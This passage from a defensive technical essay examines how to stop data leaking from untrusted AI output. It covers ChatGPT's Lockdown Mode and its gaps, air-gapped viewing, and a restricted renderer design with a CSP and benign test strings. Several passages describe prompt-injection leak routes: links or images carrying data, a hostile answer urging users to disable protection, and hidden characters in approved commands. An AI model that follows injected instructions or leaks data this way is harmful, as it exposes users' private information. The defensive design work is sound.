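OpenAI also uses the name Lockdown Mode for a setting that prevents leaks. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced the setting on 13 February for enterprise, education and healthcare plans, and an update on 4 June extended it to personal accounts.

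In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT limits browsing to cached copies of web pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, ChatGPT may also stop displaying images in ordinary answers, though users can still upload and generate them. Agent mode, deep research and file downloads are off, and users cannot give code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editor, network access.

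OpenAI calls the setting deterministic, meaning that fixed software rules enforce it whatever the model does. Like a CSP, it therefore works even when the model follows every hostile instruction. Cached browsing also hides which of an attacker's pages the model opens, as long as the attacker cannot see which cached copies it reads.

OpenAI does not guarantee that data cannot leak. It names enabled apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques as remaining risks, and the setting leaves several openings:

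- In company workspaces, Lockdown Mode does not automatically disable every app. Administrators choose the apps, and OpenAI advises against any action whose result an attacker might be able to see.
- The setting does not change network access in Codex, so it would probably not have stopped the leak that PromptArmor found there.
- OpenAI's list of restrictions does not mention ordinary links. A user who clicks one with data in its address could presumably still send that data.
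- Personal users can turn the setting off for a single chat, which a hostile answer could ask them to do.

Injected instructions still reach the model through cached pages and uploaded files, and can make its answers wrong. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* nevertheless calls the tradeoff worthwhile for anyone with sensitive data. That seems right, but the argument is based on how Lockdown Mode works, and neither OpenAI's announcement nor its documentation reports tests against real attacks.

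### A machine without a network

A simpler proposal is to view untrusted output in any renderer on a computer with no network connection. This stops every outbound request at the time of viewing, including name lookups and requests that a CSP would miss. It does not improve the other two properties.

A malicious file can still take over the viewer. It can then change later documents on the screen or infect the next USB stick. Calif's PDF reached the phone over a direct link between two devices, so a file can be dangerous without coming from the internet, though the rest of the attack may have needed a connection.

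Misleading text also looks the same when the renderer is offline. If a reviewer approves a command containing a hidden character, the command does its damage later on a machine with network access.

Opening an HTML report offline may only delay its requests for remote images. The reviewer sees an empty space where an image should be, but if they forward the report to a colleague, the colleague's browser requests the image and sends any data in its address. Pasting a suspicious link into a messaging app that fetches previews also sends a request, along with any data in the link.

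An offline machine is most useful if little data leaves it. If a team numbers 1,000 items, and for each one the machine may output only the number and a verdict of "approve" or "reject", a hijacked machine could send at most log₂ 2,000 ≈ 11 bits per item. It could still falsify the verdict, so the reviewer should enter the verdict by hand on another computer. The team can also restore the machine from a clean copy after each batch.

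### A level-3 renderer in detail

The following design shows a model's answers in a web page, for people who have to judge them. It recognises structure only at the start of a line:

| Start of the line | Display |
|---|---|
| One to three `#` signs and a space | A heading, at most 1.3 times the normal text size |
| A hyphen and a space, or a number with a full stop and a space | A list item, with two spaces of indentation for each level |
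| A vertical bar | A table row, with a new cell at each further bar |
| Three backticks | The start or end of a code block, with any other text on the line as a caption |
| Anything else | Ordinary text with its own spaces and line breaks |

The renderer ignores formatting notation within a line, so asterisks, brackets and HTML tags appear as the model wrote them. The parser needs to track little more than whether it is inside a code block. Later text cannot change the meaning of a finished line, and the renderer shows an unfinished line as ordinary text, so a partial answer is never more dangerous than the complete one.

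Because such a parser has a fixed number of states, an algorithm can check whether two of them produce the same result for every input. This is harder to check for CommonMark parsers.

The renderer creates only `h1` to `h3`, `p`, `ul`, `ol`, `li`, `table`, `tr`, `td`, `pre` and `span` elements. It takes no attributes from the content. A button switches to the level-2 view of the same bytes.

**Characters.** The viewer draws letters, digits, punctuation, symbols and ordinary spaces from one fixed version of Unicode. A tab appears as a grey arrow. Everything else, including invalid bytes and all other blank characters, appears as a code in a coloured box that the content cannot imitate. Three further rules apply:

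- The viewer draws a zero-width non-joiner normally between two letters that would otherwise connect, and a joiner normally inside an emoji on Unicode's published list.
- From the fifth combining mark on a letter, each mark appears as a code.
- A dotted line appears under any word that mixes Latin letters with Cyrillic or Greek ones. Words such as `HTTPОтвет` get it too, which is why it is only a hint.

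**Content Security Policy.** The page's server sends this policy:

`default-src 'none'; script-src 'self'; style-src 'self'; connect-src 'self'; base-uri 'none'; form-action 'none'; frame-ancestors 'none'; require-trusted-types-for 'script'; trusted-types 'none'`

The three entries with `'self'` let the page load its own scripts and styles and receive the answer. `base-uri` and `form-action` need their own entries because `default-src` does not cover them, and `frame-ancestors` keeps other sites from embedding the page. Browsers that support the last two directives block the renderer's own code from turning a string into HTML, so a programmer who later tries this will notice at once.

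**Limits.** The viewer displays up to 100,000 bytes of an answer per page, or about 16,000 English words. Longer answers continue on further pages, and the viewer shows the page count. Lists have at most four levels and tables at most 20 columns. A line that exceeds a limit appears as ordinary text, so the viewer never drops content. Each byte creates at most a few elements, so a short answer cannot expand into billions of them.

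When a user copies text, the renderer replaces hidden characters with visible codes. It also changes `https` to `hxxps` so that a messaging app does not recognise the address. A separate command shows a warning, then copies the exact bytes.

A developer can check the renderer with harmless strings. Square brackets around a code stand for the coloured box, and names in braces stand for single characters or bytes:

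| Input | Expected display |
|---|---|
| `Lunch is at the [café](PAGE). ![map](PICTURE)` | The same characters, with nothing to click and no request in the browser's network log |
| `<b>lunch</b>` | The same characters, with both tags visible |
| `&ouml;` | The same six characters, not ö |
| `noon{BACKSPACE}one` | `noon[U+0008]one` |
| `lun{ZERO-WIDTH SPACE}ch` | `lun[U+200B]ch` |
| `{RIGHT-TO-LEFT OVERRIDE}abc` | `[U+202E]abc`, in that order |
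| `{BYTE FF}lunch` | `[FF]lunch` |
| A Persian verb with a non-joiner after its prefix | The correctly spelled word, without a code |
| `# Menu`, before the line break arrives | Ordinary text, which becomes a heading when the line ends |
| A list item at the fifth level | Ordinary text, with its hyphen and indentation |
| "cocoa" with a Cyrillic first letter | The word with a dotted line under it |
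| "cocoa" entirely in Cyrillic letters | The word without a dotted line |

The last string tests a known gap. The viewer would be useless to Russian readers if it marked every Cyrillic word as suspicious, so someone checking a name or web address should switch to the ASCII view, which shows the Cyrillic word's ten bytes as ten codes.
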